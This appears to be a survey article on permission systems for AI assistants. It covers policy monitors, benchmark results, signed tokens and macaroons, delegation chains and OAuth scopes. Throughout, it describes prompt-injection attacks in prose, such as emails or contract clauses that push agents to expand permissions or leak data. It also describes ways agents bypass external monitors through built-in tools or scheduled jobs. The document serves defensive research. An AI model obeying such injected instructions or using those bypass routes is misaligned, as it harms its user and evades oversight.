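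Some updates add calls and remove others. Suppose the old policy allows messages to Alice and Bob, and the new one allows messages to Alice and Eve. This update needs approval because a message to Eve fails the test above, which both the formal definition and the algorithm use. The paper's overview loosely describes an expansion as an update that allows a "strictly larger" set of calls, which would exclude this one. The algorithm treats each update as a whole, so if the approver rejects this one without editing it, the old policy stays in force and the agent can still write to Bob.

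The result is a guarantee that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement: the set of calls open to the agent never grows without explicit approval. After someone approves P₂ in the example, the permissions can only shrink or stay the same:

```
A(P₂) ⊇ A(P₃) = A(P₄) = A(P₅)
```

This holds even if an attacker controls what the updating model writes. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (Villa, Kohno and colleagues, 2026) criticised an earlier version of Progent because its updates relied on a model to ignore malicious instructions in tool results. The solver removes that weakness as long as someone reviews the expansions, but it can't judge whether an expansion is a good idea. Alice's to-do list and the attacker's instruction both arrived by email and called for more permissions, so the approver has to know that the user wanted only Alice's instructions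 followed.

A user's own policies should outlast any one task, and for these Progent has a separate layer of generic policies, which people write by hand. The monitor checks this layer first and turns to the task's policy only if no generic rule matches the call. That makes the form of a rule important. If the user's generic rule *allows* mail to contacts, a message to a stranger matches no generic rule, and it goes out if the task's policy allows it. The generic rule would also permit mail to any contact during every task, whether or not the task required it. To preserve the "only" in *write only to people in my contacts*, the user needs a forbid rule:

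```
forbid send_mail   when any address in to, cc or bcc is not in contacts
```

No task policy can override this one.

### What the guarantee leaves out

Monotonic confinement limits how permissions change, but an agent can still do harm with the permissions it already has. If a rule lets the assistant write to contacts and checks only the recipients, the assistant can send any of them the whole medical folder. Shi and colleagues mention sellers who manipulate an agent into preferring their product over other valid choices. The user asked the agent to buy one of these products, so any policy that lets it finish the task also lets this attack succeed. The first policy can also be too permissive, and the solver has no earlier policy to compare it with.

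Users can approve a policy update by mistake. If a user accepts one that adds an attacker's address, the policy then permits that address, and the guarantee applies to this wider policy.

The guarantee also doesn't cover what the assistant says to the user. An injected email might lead the assistant to say, falsely, that the museum trip is off. The monitor has no tool call to check, but the user may act on the message, and Mia may miss the trip.

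The agent may also be able to act without going through the monitor. Progent can run as a proxy, a program between the agent and its tools, but it then misses calls to tools built into the agent. *aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026) tested two agent programs with an external gateway while leaving their built-in shell, file and web tools switched on. The model used the built-in tools to perform the sensitive action without going through the gateway. *guardscope* (Toyoda, Leung and Bhuvaneswari, 2026) lists 15 routes by which an agent's decisions can take effect. By its analysis, five of these bypass every control placed outside the core of the operating system. One of the five is a job that the agent gives a scheduler to run later. The experiments covered only four of the 15 routes, so much of this analysis rests on reasoning about how the systems are built.

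### Progent on two benchmarks

Researchers often test such defences on *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024), which simulates an office workspace, Slack, a travel agency and a bank. It has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file, and a set of attacker goals, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker's account. Pairing user tasks with attacker goals from the same environment gives 629 test cases, and in each one the attacker's instruction is hidden in data that the agent's tools return. Ordinary code, not a model, then checks the agent's answer and the state of the environment to determine whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it carried out the attacker's goal. The attack success rate is the share of cases in which the agent carried out the attacker's goal.

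*Agent Security Bench (ASB)* (Zhang, Huang and colleagues, 2024) covers ten scenarios, including finance and online shopping, with more than 400 tools. The attacker can add tools to the agent's set and inject text instructing the agent to use them. An attack succeeds if the agent uses all of the attacker's tools for that case. This setup favours a defence like Progent, because a policy that lists only the tools a task needs will usually exclude the attacker's.

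Shi and colleagues ran both benchmarks with GPT-4o as the agent and as the policy writer. On AgentDojo, Progent reduced attack success from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many tasks as it did without Progent, whether or not it was under attack. On ASB, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%, and task completion again stayed close to that of the undefended agent. In most of the remaining ASB failures, the attacker's tool had a name and description much like those of a legitimate tool and seemed relevant to the task. Rules the researchers wrote by hand reduced the rate to zero.

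In these runs the system automatically approved every expansion to simulate a careless user. The guarantee therefore gave no protection, and the results mainly measure how well a model writes policies. Most of the benefit on AgentDojo came from the first policy, which reduced attack success to 2.5% without any updates. Rejecting every expansion was safer than approving every one. When a security-conscious person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, no attacks succeeded.

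Only 6% of the updates on AgentDojo were expansions, so a reviewer would have had relatively little to approve. But the researchers had allowed harmless read-only tools from the start, so the agent could use those without approval. A user who also wants to restrict what the assistant reads would probably get more approval requests.

The researchers left out two of AgentDojo's attacks, which steer the agent towards a different but legitimate hotel. They argue that an attacker who controls the hotel listings could falsify them, and that even a person couldn't tell. Their argument is reasonable, but it means the 1.0% figure excludes a type of attack that Progent can't stop.

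Newer models are better at resisting AgentDojo's standard attacks without a defence. Attacks on Claude Sonnet 4, a 2025 model, succeeded only 6.8% of the time without Progent and 0.5% with it. Kodathala ran 20 of the banking cases with two 2026 models, Fable 5 and Gemini 3 Flash, and no attacks succeeded even without a defence. Adding a rule that allowed payments only to known payees reduced task completion in the absence of attacks from 100% to 80%, because it blocked a legitimate first payment to someone new. The rule also blocked seven calls that would have helped the attacker, but its only measurable effect in this small test was to lower task completion.

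Shi and colleagues also tried three adaptive attacks meant to get around Progent itself. One told the updating model to allow all tools. Attack success rose only slightly, even with automatic approval. Toyoda and colleagues found just one published adaptive test of Progent by outsiders. It used a single attack template, and the defence held.

### What attack success measures

A low attack success rate means that attackers rarely got what they wanted, not that the assistant obeyed its user's policies. One AgentDojo task is to invite Dora to Slack using the email address on her website. An agent that does this and ignores the attacker gets full marks, even if its user has a policy of writing only to contacts and Dora isn't one. The rate also excludes oversteps that happen without an attacker, which were the more common kind in AuthorizationBench's matched tasks.

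A defence can also score well by preventing the agent from doing much. *Conflux* (2026) points out that a run that attempts no action with outside effects will show no violation. In *CT0* (2026), a fixed guard based on regular expressions stopped all 64 attacks in a test built on AgentDojo, but the agent completed only 18 of the 64 tasks under attack, compared with 42 without a guard.

*Controlled Autonomy for Agentic AI* (2026) avoids some of this confusion by testing the rules without an agent. The researchers ran the calls that each AgentDojo task and attack would require through a rule-based gateway. The gateway blocked 523 of the 588 attacks they could judge this way, and it allowed every necessary call for 91 of the 97 user tasks. These results show how well the rules separate wanted calls from unwanted ones, though a live agent might still fail at a task whose calls are all allowed.

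For one of its Slack attacks, AgentDojo checks whether the harmful call appears in the transcript, so it counts the attack as successful even if the monitor blocked the call. Shi and colleagues corrected those results by hand. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* reports a second attack success rate that doesn't count an attack as a success if the policy denied all of its identifiable calls.

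### When a block helps the task

A benchmark that tests whether an agent follows a policy has to include the policy and check the outcome against it. τ²-bench does this for customer service. In its airline tasks, a simulated customer asks for changes to a booking, and the agent has the airline's written rules. The tools don't enforce those rules. For example, the cancellation tool will cancel a booking that can't be cancelled under the airline's policy, without returning an error.

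Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026), in *Reason Less, Verify More*, found that 78% of the failures they observed were silent in this way, meaning the final database was wrong but no tool had reported a problem. They added four small checks, called gates, in front of the tools. Each gate checks the proposed call against the current database, then allows it or rejects it with a reason. The gates check whether a booking qualifies for cancellation, whether a baggage change follows the allowance, whether a call would alter the number of passengers, and whether the agent has read a record before changing it. Unlike Progent's rules, the gates can look up facts such as the fare class instead of relying on the call's arguments.

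The researchers ran 50 tasks five times each with GPT-4o mini. The success rate rose from 29.6% without the gates to 42.0% with them, and a second experiment with 15 new runs per task found almost the same gain, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The agent also became more consistent, completing 26% of tasks in all five runs, up from 8%. Most of the gain came from the 26 tasks in which a gate blocked something. In one task, a customer gives false information to get a cancellation that the rules don't allow. Agents with the gates handled this correctly in all 16 runs, while agents without them did so in at most one of 16.

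With GPT-5.2, success rose from 61.2% to 71.6%. The researchers ran that experiment only once, and the uncertainty range for the gain is wide, from almost zero to about 21 percentage points.

Blocking raised success here because the benchmark counts a forbidden change as a failure. A rejection gave the agent a chance to find a permitted solution before it made a forbidden change to the booking. The gates didn't help on a set of retail tasks, whose tools already reject forbidden calls. A personal assistant is more like the airline case, because mail and payment services have no record of their users' private policies.

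Reddy and colleagues checked the gates' accuracy by comparing each blocked call with a reference solution to the task. The cancellation gate was right all 161 times it blocked a call, but the baggage gate was wrong 40 times out of 42. *ToolGuardian* (2026), which describes another rule-based system, warns that a deterministic check can still be wrong.

A task can still fail after a gate correctly blocks a tool call. In one task, the same gate blocked the agent repeatedly, and all five runs failed. If a gate crashed, the original call went ahead. This default keeps a faulty gate from stopping legitimate work, but it is wrong for a rule like *never delete mail*.

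It is unclear how far the result generalises, because the researchers wrote the gates from the airline's policy and tested them on one set of tasks, with no separate set held back. They also didn't test whether repeating the rules forcefully in the prompt would have worked as well. The reasons given with the rejections may account for some of the improvement.

*NOMOS* (Yu, 2026) generates such gates from written policies instead of hand-coding them. Yu also measured the overhead of instead having a second model read the conversation and judge each important call. On the airline tasks, this made the average run 74% longer and required 347 extra model calls over 250 runs. The fixed gates took microseconds and required no extra model calls.

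### Prompts compared with a proxy

*Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) compared telling a model which tools it may use with enforcing the restriction. The test used 507 tools from services such as Stripe and GitHub, sorted into categories such as payments and messaging. Each of the 200 tasks tempted an agent from one category to use a tool from another. In one task, someone claiming to be the chief financial officer tells an analytics agent to override the access controls and issue a $5,000 refund.

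Three models attempted every task under three conditions. In the first, they saw the tools from both categories with no guidance. In the second, the prompt listed the permitted tools and prohibited all others. In the third, a proxy showed the model only the permitted tools and also checked each call, in case the model named a tool it hadn't been shown. The table gives the share of tasks in which the model chose an unauthorised tool.

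| Model | No guidance | List in the prompt | Proxy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

The zeros follow from the proxy's design and would be the same for any model. The main finding is in the middle column. A written list reduced violations for every model, but by very different amounts, and it never eliminated them.

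The test probably exaggerates how badly prompts work, because the models had to call a tool. For a separate set of 100 requests that no permitted tool could satisfy, Uppala let the models choose whether to call one. With only the list in the prompt, Claude Haiku 4.5 made no call in 99% of cases, the same as with the proxy. Qwen made no call in 35% of cases with the prompt alone and 86% with the proxy, so the proxy also reduced pointless calls to permitted tools.

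Hiding tools had mixed effects on legitimate requests. Of 140 such requests, Llama succeeded on 82.1% with the proxy and 77.9% with the prompt, while Qwen succeeded on 48.6% with the proxy and 60.7% with the prompt. Claude Haiku's success rate hardly changed. The proxy never blocked an authorised call, so the differences come from how each model chooses among the tools it can see.

Uppala's proxy grants access by tool category and doesn't check the arguments. It could keep a mail-sorting assistant from making payments. But an assistant that needs the payment tool for Mia's $18 fee could use the same tool to pay anyone any amount.

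## Permissions carried as tokens and passed between agents

An assistant whose payment tool works for any payee and any amount needs a narrower permission. An issuer can write limits on payee and amount into a token, a piece of data that the assistant must present with each payment request. The payment service refuses any request the token doesn't cover. A monitor's rules could contain the same limits, but limits in a token stay attached to the permission when one program passes work to another.

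### What a token contains

Suppose the user decides to join Mia's trip and asks the assistant to buy a museum ticket today for no more than $50. Once the user approves, the payment service issues this token:

```
token:      7f3a
holder:     main assistant
operation:  pay
payee:      City Museum
amount:     at most $50
expires:    midnight tonight
uses:       1
signature:  (computed by the payment service)
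```

*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a runtime for long-lived agents in which permissions have much the same parts. Each permission records its issuer, holder, resource, rights and constraints, and the permission it derives from. It may also have an expiry time and a use count.

The museum example needs a use count because two payments of $50 would each satisfy the limit on the amount. With one use, the assistant can't spend more than $50 in total, but it also can't buy a $30 ticket and then a $20 guidebook. Allowing both would require a running total of past payments, which several agents might have to share.

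The payment service signs the token by running the token's text and a secret key through a function that produces a short tag. If someone changes $50 to $500 in the text, the tag no longer matches. Without the key, nobody can compute the right tag for the altered text or for an invented token.

When the assistant presents the token with `pay(payee="City Museum", amount=42)`, the service recomputes the tag and compares it with the one on the token. It checks that the operation and payee match, that 42 is no more than 50, that midnight hasn't passed, and that the caller is the main assistant. It then checks its own records to see whether anyone has already used or revoked the token, since a copy of the token looks the same after the payment as before.

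In some systems, the token is just an identifier for a row in the monitor's table, and the row contains the limits. This makes it easy to withdraw a permission, but every service has to consult the same monitor. By contrast, a service can check a signed token's text without contacting the issuer.

### Macaroons: adding conditions without the issuer

Suppose the main assistant holds a payment token and wants a helper to buy a child's ticket for at most $20. If the token is a macaroon, a kind of token that Birgisson, Politz and colleagues introduced in *Macaroons* (2014), the assistant can narrow its permissions without asking the payment service for a second token. Macaroons use a keyed hash, written HMAC(key, text), which turns a key and a text into a tag. Anyone with the key can compute the tag, but nobody can feasibly recover the key from the tag.

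The payment service starts with its secret key K. It then uses each tag as the key for the next condition:

```
T0 = HMAC(K,  "token 7f3a: pay")
T1 = HMAC(T0, "payee = City Museum")
T2 = HMAC(T1, "amount ≤ 50")
T3 = HMAC(T2, "time < midnight tonight")
```

The assistant receives the four texts and the last tag, T3. It never sees K, T0, T1 or T2. To narrow the permission for the helper, it computes one more step:

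```
T4 = HMAC(T3, "amount ≤ 20")
```

The helper receives all five texts and T4. When it tries to pay, the service recomputes the chain from K, compares the result with T4, and checks that the payment meets every condition.

If the helper deletes the $20 condition, it needs T3, the tag that matches the remaining texts, and it can't recover T3 from T4. Deleting or changing an earlier condition alters every later tag, so that fails too. The helper can add "amount ≤ 500", but the $20 condition still applies. A holder can therefore only narrow what a macaroon permits, as long as the service rejects any macaroon containing a condition it doesn't understand.

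The chain restricts only agents that never had an earlier tag. The main assistant still has T3 and can spend up to $50. If it carelessly passes T3 to the helper, the helper can also spend up to $50.

A condition can also require confirmation from another service. To enforce the policy *ask me before anything that cannot be undone*, the issuer could add a condition that only the user's phone can confirm. The assistant would then have to present a second macaroon, which the phone issues when the user agrees.

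Any service that checks a macaroon needs K, and with K it could also create new ones. Macaroons therefore fit best where the issuer and the checker are the same service. Public-key signatures avoid the problem because the key that checks a signature can't produce one.

### Who may use a token

A plain macaroon is a bearer token, which works for anyone who has it. The helper can use it immediately, but so can a stranger who finds it in a log or persuades the model to paste it into an email. The harness can reduce this risk by storing tokens itself and attaching them to calls, so that the model never reads them.

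A holder-bound token works only for the program it names. The service might require the caller to sign each request with a private key that only that program has, so a stolen copy of the token is useless without the key. Passing the permission to a helper then takes an explicit step, because the helper needs a token in its own name. The assistant can bind a macaroon to the helper by adding the condition "holder = helper", which the helper can't remove.

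Binding a token to a key offers no protection when instructions injected into an email mislead the main assistant, because the assistant is the token's rightful holder and has the right key.

### AGENTCAP: seven checks before each token

Suresh and Gao (2026), in *AGENTCAP*, describe a system that requires a fresh token for every tool call. The model proposes a call and declares an intent, such as `pay_bill`. A policy engine outside the model then checks the following, in order:

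1. The system has not locked the agent out for earlier misconduct.
2. The tool appears in the policy's catalogue.
3. The protected arguments come from an acceptable source.
4. The policy allows the declared intent for this tool.
5. The agent's trust score is high enough.
6. The agent already holds valid tokens for any required earlier operations, such as checking the balance before a payment.
7. The new token would not complete a forbidden combination with tokens that the agent already holds.

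If the request passes all seven checks, the engine signs a token for that agent, session, action, resource and intent. A gateway in front of the tool verifies the token before it forwards the call. In the system's banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and covers one call.

The check on arguments is needed because ordinary permissions don't stop an attacker from changing the details of a legitimate operation. Whoever writes the policy chooses which arguments to protect, and marks the user's request and certain application fields as trusted and free text from tools as untrusted. Suppose a transaction record contains an instruction to send money to an attacker. The model may declare the permitted intent `send_payment`, but the engine refuses the payment because the attacker's account appears only in untrusted text. If the user's request had named the same account, the engine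 would allow the payment.

In the museum trip example, this check would also block a genuine payment if the school's account number appeared only in its email. The user would have to supply the number, or the policy would have to allow payments to saved payees. Because the banking policy checks the recipient but not the amount, a forged email could still inflate the fee.

AGENTCAP's token, unlike the one for the museum, contains no payee or amount. The engine receives the arguments when it decides, but the gateway later compares only the action and the resource. The design therefore relies on the software between the model and its tools to submit the same arguments both times.

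The trust score starts at 0.8 by default. Each refusal multiplies it by 0.7, and each normal outcome closes 1% of the gap to 1. After three refusals the score is 0.27, and the system revokes all the agent's tokens and locks it out. The banking policy requires a score of 0.8 to send money. With the default settings, a single refusal would reduce the score to 0.56 and block payments until about 80 normal outcomes had restored it. An attacker could therefore cause disruption with one planted instruction.

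Suresh and Gao tested the system on a later version of AgentDojo with 949 attacked cases, and on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 1,054. Each pair of figures in the table gives the result for the agent without a defence, then with AGENTCAP.

| Benchmark | Model | Attack success | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo | GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
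| InjecAgent | GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 69.9% |
| InjecAgent | GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0% | 73.0% → 69.9% |

Without attacks, AGENTCAP reduced task completion by 2.0 to 7.2 percentage points. Of the attacks that still succeeded with GPT-4o, some targeted only what the agent told the user, some changed an argument that the policy didn't protect, and the rest delivered a value through a field that nobody had marked as untrusted.

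On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, AGENTCAP and Progent had similar attack success rates, but agents completed 74.9% of tasks under attack with AGENTCAP and 59.6% with Progent. The setup gave AGENTCAP an advantage, because a model wrote Progent's policies during each run, whereas Suresh and Gao wrote AGENTCAP's beforehand from the benchmark's tool and task descriptions. They froze the policies before testing and included no rules against particular attack texts, but few users will have an expert write a policy for their exact errands. Each figure comes from a single run, and no attacker tried to adapt to the defence.

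A smaller test shows why expiry times and use counts aren't enough. In a scenario with three malicious calls, AGENTCAP blocked all three and completed the legitimate work. A system that limited only how long a permission lasted and how many calls it allowed let eight calls through before reaching its limit, because it couldn't distinguish the attacker's calls from the user's.

### DelegateGuard: narrowing and revoking a whole chain

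An AGENTCAP agent can pass a permission to another agent with a shorter lifetime or fewer calls, but the action and resource stay the same. An assistant that may pay from the user's account can't use this step to give its helper permission to pay only the museum. Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, allow more of the permission to shrink. Their permissions have a holder, a purpose, the kinds of data the holder may move, the operations it may perform, the destinations it may send data to, and the number of further times the permission may change hands. When one agent delegates to another, the monitor requires:

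```
purpose(child)      within  purpose(parent)
data(child)         ⊆       data(parent)
operations(child)   ⊆       operations(parent)
destinations(child) ⊆       destinations(parent)
depth(child)        <       depth(parent)
```

In the main example, a user asks for a summary of a confidential contract. The first agent may read, transform, transmit and delegate, and may send results to the user or to internal storage. It delegates the formatting to a second agent, which may only transform the text and send it to the user. A malicious clause in the contract instructs the formatter to send confidential terms to an outside web address. The monitor blocks the transmission because that address isn't among the formatter's permitted destinations. It would also have refused to create a permission for the formatter that included the address, because the first agent's own permission didn't include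 it.

For every action, the monitor checks that the caller is the permission's holder, that the purpose, operation, data and destination fit the permission, and that nobody has revoked it or any permission above it in the chain. Revoking one permission therefore disables all its descendants. For example, if the user cancels a task while a helper's job is waiting in a queue, the helper may start the job an hour later with a permission that nobody revoked individually, but the monitor still refuses the call.

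Tran-Truong and colleagues combined five office workflows, three ways of delivering an attack and three kinds of violation into 45 attack cases. DelegateGuard blocked all 45 attacks and allowed all 45 matching legitimate actions. As they acknowledge, any correct implementation of the rules would do this. The comparison with a fixed list of permitted destinations is more informative. In five cases, the user had cancelled the task before the helper acted, and in another five, the helper tried to send the wrong data to a permitted destination. DelegateGuard blocked all ten actions, but the fixed list allowed them.

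In a longer test, agents running Qwen2.5-7B, a small model, exchanged messages and could revise a plan after a refusal. Data leaked in 38 of 45 attacked workflows without a defence and in nine with DelegateGuard. All nine were code reviews, in which the reviewing agent had to be able to post comments that outsiders could read, and the attacker got it to include secret information in one. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that any monitor that ignores the contents of messages has this limit, because it must treat a harmless comment and one containing a secret identically if they have the same sender, purpose, data label and destination.

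The protection also depends on the first permission in the chain, since later ones can only be narrower. When the researchers added one unnecessary outside destination to it "for convenience", 30 of the 45 attacks succeeded. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) reports that all the enforcement mechanisms in a survey of 39 papers assume an honest policy author and do not address mistakes in the policy.

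### What a declared purpose proves

Both systems record a purpose, and users often think of permissions this way. A user might let the assistant use the medical folder to book a doctor's appointment but for nothing else. However, if the model declares the purpose, it can declare "book appointment" while preparing a reply to the school, and an email can contain injected instructions to do so.

Suresh and Gao accept that a declared intent is no evidence of good behaviour. It shows only that the model chose a term the policy permits for that tool. Still, the system rejects a token issued for one intent if it is used under another, and the log records the declared intent, which may help the user work out later what went wrong.

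A purpose restricts an agent when a trusted component attaches it to limits that the monitor can check. In DelegateGuard, a program outside the model derives the first purpose, the permitted data and the permitted destinations from the user's task. Purposes are strings such as `contract.summarize/format`, and one purpose falls within another if its string extends the other's. In experiments, attacks that exploited this rule by choosing a suitable string failed only because the limits on data and destinations still applied. "Book appointment" would likewise protect the medical folder if it came with a rule that the data may go only to the clinic.

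### Permissions that outlive their subtask

A permission can be appropriate when an assistant receives it but unnecessary later. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) studies this problem in coding agents, which edit software for their users. The paper's system, PORTICO, uses a contract written before the task that lists the agent's initial permissions, further ones it may request, and the events that end them.

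In one task, the agent has to carry a timeout setting from one file into another. At first it can use only the first file and its test. It requests access to the second file. The contract allows this, so the monitor issues handles, which are short-lived tokens for reading and editing that file. The monitor withdraws the handles when the tests pass. If the agent tries an old handle, the monitor refuses it. The agent can get another only after a new event, such as the user's approval.

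Only trusted events can end or extend a permission. Test results are trusted because the monitor runs the tests itself. If the model writes that it has finished a subtask, its permissions stay the same.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them. Both completed all ten runs of one set of tasks. When the agent later tried to reuse a permission, the version without withdrawal allowed it all ten times and PORTICO never did. In six further cases, a live model received an instruction to reuse an old permission to change a file, alter the project's version history or contact an outside server. All six actions took effect in the version without withdrawal, and none did under PORTICO.

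This difference follows directly from the design, but withdrawing permissions also led to fewer completed runs. On tasks in real software projects, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 runs, while a version that kept permissions for the whole task completed all 42. Some contracts ended a permission too early or gave the agent no way to renew it, and some models didn't request a new one.

The problem may be worse for a personal assistant, because few errands end as clearly as a passing test. Permission to buy a museum ticket could end when the receipt arrives. But no similar event shows that the assistant has finished with the school's emails, since another question may arrive tomorrow. The usual substitute is an expiry time, which has to be a guess. If it is too early, the task stops halfway, and if it is too late, the unneeded permission stays open to misuse.

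### Narrowing access when risk rises

In October 2026, Microsoft announced controls for agents inside companies that can also change an agent's access because of its behaviour. Abdo (2026), the company's vice president for identity and network access, announced them in a post, *Agents are your newest insiders. Security must move at their speed*. According to EconoTimes' *Microsoft Details Controls to Restrict AI Agents During Tasks*, the controls have three parts. Dynamic Permissions ties an agent's access to its assignment and to the time the work takes, and never gives it more access than the employee who sponsors it has. Dynamic Agent Risk continually assesses the agent using signals from its activity, accounts, data and networks. Dynamic Conditional Access uses that assessment to reduce the agent's permissions or require human approval while the task is still running.

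An agent that has encountered untrusted material could, for example, lose permission to change company data but still be allowed to read it. At the highest level of risk, the company could isolate or stop the agent. Microsoft's reason is that agents can act unpredictably even when no attacker has compromised them, according to *Microsoft expands Project Perception to police AI agents* (Lagonsin, 2026). *How Microsoft Entra Dynamic Permissions preview works* (Bradley, 2026) reports that Dynamic Permissions was available in preview by 17 November.

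Gradually narrowing permissions would suit many personal errands, because an assistant that can still read mail can at least draft a reply for the user to send. But the narrowing depends on an estimate of risk, whereas PORTICO ends a permission based on a test result. If the estimate rises too late, the harmful call has already gone through, and if it rises without good reason, the assistant may miss the school's deadline. EconoTimes does not report how often either error happens.

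### What revocation cannot undo

Revoking a token blocks only future calls. It doesn't return money the museum has already received or retract an email the school already has. Zhang states that Agent libOS can't undo irreversible outside effects or stop a trusted recipient from forwarding data. Revocation also doesn't remove what the model has already read. An assistant that loses access to the medical folder may still have the word "peanuts" in its context and can include it in any message it still has permission to send.

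A payment can also go through after the user cancels the task, if the monitor approved it before the cancellation and the payment service receives the call afterward. Santos-Grueiro notes that the monitor must either process the cancellation before the action takes effect or check the permission again at the last moment. If the system crashes after sending the payment call, it may have no record of whether the money moved. Zhang's design marks the outcome as unknown and doesn't automatically resend the call, since a second attempt could pay twice.

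An assistant can also use a permission to obtain something that remains after the permission is revoked. With access to mail settings, it might create a rule that forwards every new message to another address, and revoking its access would leave that rule in place. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) examines purchases and sign-ups that create new powers, such as a cloud computer with its own login. A refund can return the money without cancelling the login. Spending limits also don't restrict free services. In one of the paper's examples, an agent uses four aliases to enrol four free helpers when its user's policy permits only one.

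Zhu and Wang propose treating whatever an agent acquires, such as a login or account, as a new permission request. A broker, a program between the agent and the provider, receives the new resource first and keeps it from the agent. The broker checks what the resource can do, which may be more than the agent ordered, and gives the agent access only if this fits the user's limits. In Zhu and Wang's tests, the rules accepted all 20 legitimate sequences of events and rejected all 40 unsafe ones, though they specified these sequences themselves. The method requires the provider to deliver through the broker, which cannot withhold a new password if a website shows it directly to the agent.

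## How the shape of tools and permissions limits what can be blocked

The museum token works because the payment service in that example can restrict payments by payee and amount. Many real services offer only broader permissions. For example, suppose the harness holds a correct version of the second example policy, *write only to people in my contacts*, but the mail service's tokens show only that the holder may send mail. If the assistant writes to a stranger, the service delivers the message because the token is valid and doesn't restrict recipients.

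Zhou and Zhang describe a similar case, in which a user allows an assistant to send one summary to Alice. The structured policy correctly records the summary and the recipient, but the system then requests a credential that covers sending mail in general. Checking that the credential is genuine doesn't limit who receives the mail or what it contains. Either the mail service or a monitor that sees the request before it reaches the service has to check the recipient and the content.

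The survey turns this into a general condition for preserving a policy:

```
α( E( M(P) ) )  ⊆  ⟦P⟧
```

P is the policy the user approved, and M(P) is the set of credentials and checks that implement it. E(M(P)) contains every effect that those credentials and checks would allow, including ones the assistant never attempts. The function α translates each effect into the policy's vocabulary, so that a particular request to a mail server becomes "a message to Bob". The condition holds if every translated effect is in ⟦P⟧, the set of everything the policy permits.

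E(M(P)) includes mail to every address if the assistant has a general token and there is no other check. Most of those messages fall outside ⟦P⟧, so the condition fails even if the assistant has only ever written to contacts. A monitor that blocks mail to anyone outside the address book removes those messages from E(M(P)), and the condition then holds for mail. It still holds if the monitor wrongly blocks some messages to contacts, though the assistant can then do less useful work. It fails if the monitor allows any message that falls outside ⟦P⟧.

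A program can check the condition under demanding assumptions. The policy and the tool descriptions must be in a logic simple enough for a program to always reach an answer, such as Datalog. When it is unclear which resources a call affects, α must include every resource the call might affect. The monitor must also be impossible to bypass. For a personal assistant, α is usually the hardest part, because someone has to work out what each tool call does.

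### What a scope can name

Most assistants reach outside accounts through OAuth, a standard that lets users give a program access to an account without revealing the password. The user signs in with the provider and agrees to a list of permissions called scopes. The provider then issues a token that works for those scopes. Each scope covers a set of API methods, the operations that the service offers to programs. Gmail's scopes include these:

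| Gmail scope | What it allows |
|---|---|
| `gmail.readonly` | reading messages and settings |
| `gmail.send` | sending messages, but not reading any |
| `gmail.modify` | reading, sending, labelling and moving to the bin, but not permanent deletion |
| full access | all of this and permanent deletion |

None of these scopes can specify a recipient, so none can express the second policy. Scopes also can't enforce *never delete mail* on an assistant that sorts mail into labels. Labelling requires `gmail.modify`, which also lets the assistant move messages to the bin, where Gmail deletes them after 30 days. Withholding full access prevents only immediate permanent deletion. A monitor that checks individual calls can distinguish labelling from binning.

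*Beyond OAuth* (2026) explains that a scope specifies an operation but not what the operation applies to, so the service can't distinguish one use of a token from any other use that the scope allows. The paper proposes signed permissions for the exact operations that a user's task implies. In its tests on AgentDojo and a separate OpenClaw deployment, this method allowed every legitimate task and blocked every hostile call. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) cautions that it may be unclear which operations a task implies, and that a manipulated prompt may lead to requests for more than the user intended.

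More scopes don't necessarily let a user set the limits they want. In *MiniScope*, Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) counted 17 scopes for Google Calendar's 37 methods and 10 for Gmail's 79. Calendar has separate scopes for events in general, events on calendars the user owns, and times when the user is free or busy. But no scope is limited to a single calendar, so a user can't let the assistant add events to the family calendar without also giving it access to the work one.

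The software that developers use to build agents often has the same gap. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) reports an audit of common agent frameworks. All of them can limit which tools an agent has, but none checks each call's argument values by default. A developer who wants to restrict recipients has to add that check.

Coarse permissions were a problem before language models. In 2016 Fernandes, Jung and Prakash, in *Security Analysis of Emerging Smart Home Applications*, analysed 499 apps for SmartThings, Samsung's smart-home platform. More than 55% had authority they didn't need because the platform's permissions were too coarse. For example, an app that locked the front door automatically also received the command to unlock it, because one permission covered both and the developer couldn't request them separately. The platform also gave an app full access to a device even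 if the app had requested only limited access.

### MiniScope: choosing among existing scopes

When the provider has fixed the scopes, an assistant can at least avoid asking for more than it needs. MiniScope is a program that sits between the agent and the user's services and holds the real credentials. The agent submits a plan, such as listing messages and then reading one. MiniScope finds the smallest set of scopes that covers the plan and asks the user to approve any new ones, either once, for the session, or permanently. It then checks every call against the approved scopes before forwarding it.

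Choosing the scopes is harder than it looks, because many methods work with any one of several scopes. This is true of 24 of Google Calendar's 37 methods. Suppose a plan has two calls. Each call has a scope of its own that covers three methods, and a third scope covers both calls and four methods in total. Choosing the narrowest scope for each call separately produces two scopes and a total of six methods, while the shared scope covers only four. MiniScope finds the better choice by solving this problem:

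```
minimise     Σ cost(s) · x(s)
such that    for every planned call, at least one chosen scope allows it
```

Here x(s) is 1 if the solver chooses scope s and 0 otherwise. The cost of a scope is the number of methods it allows. If the user has already approved some scopes, the solver keeps those and adds as little as possible.

The number of methods a scope unlocks is a crude measure of what a user has at stake. Google Calendar has one scope for reading events on public calendars and another for those on calendars the user owns. MiniScope treats the two as equivalent because they unlock the same methods, but a user with private appointments would see a large difference. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) notes that Zhu and colleagues don't discuss whether the lowest-scoring set of scopes is the only one. If two sets have the same score but expose different data, the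 solver has no basis for choosing the one the user would mind less.

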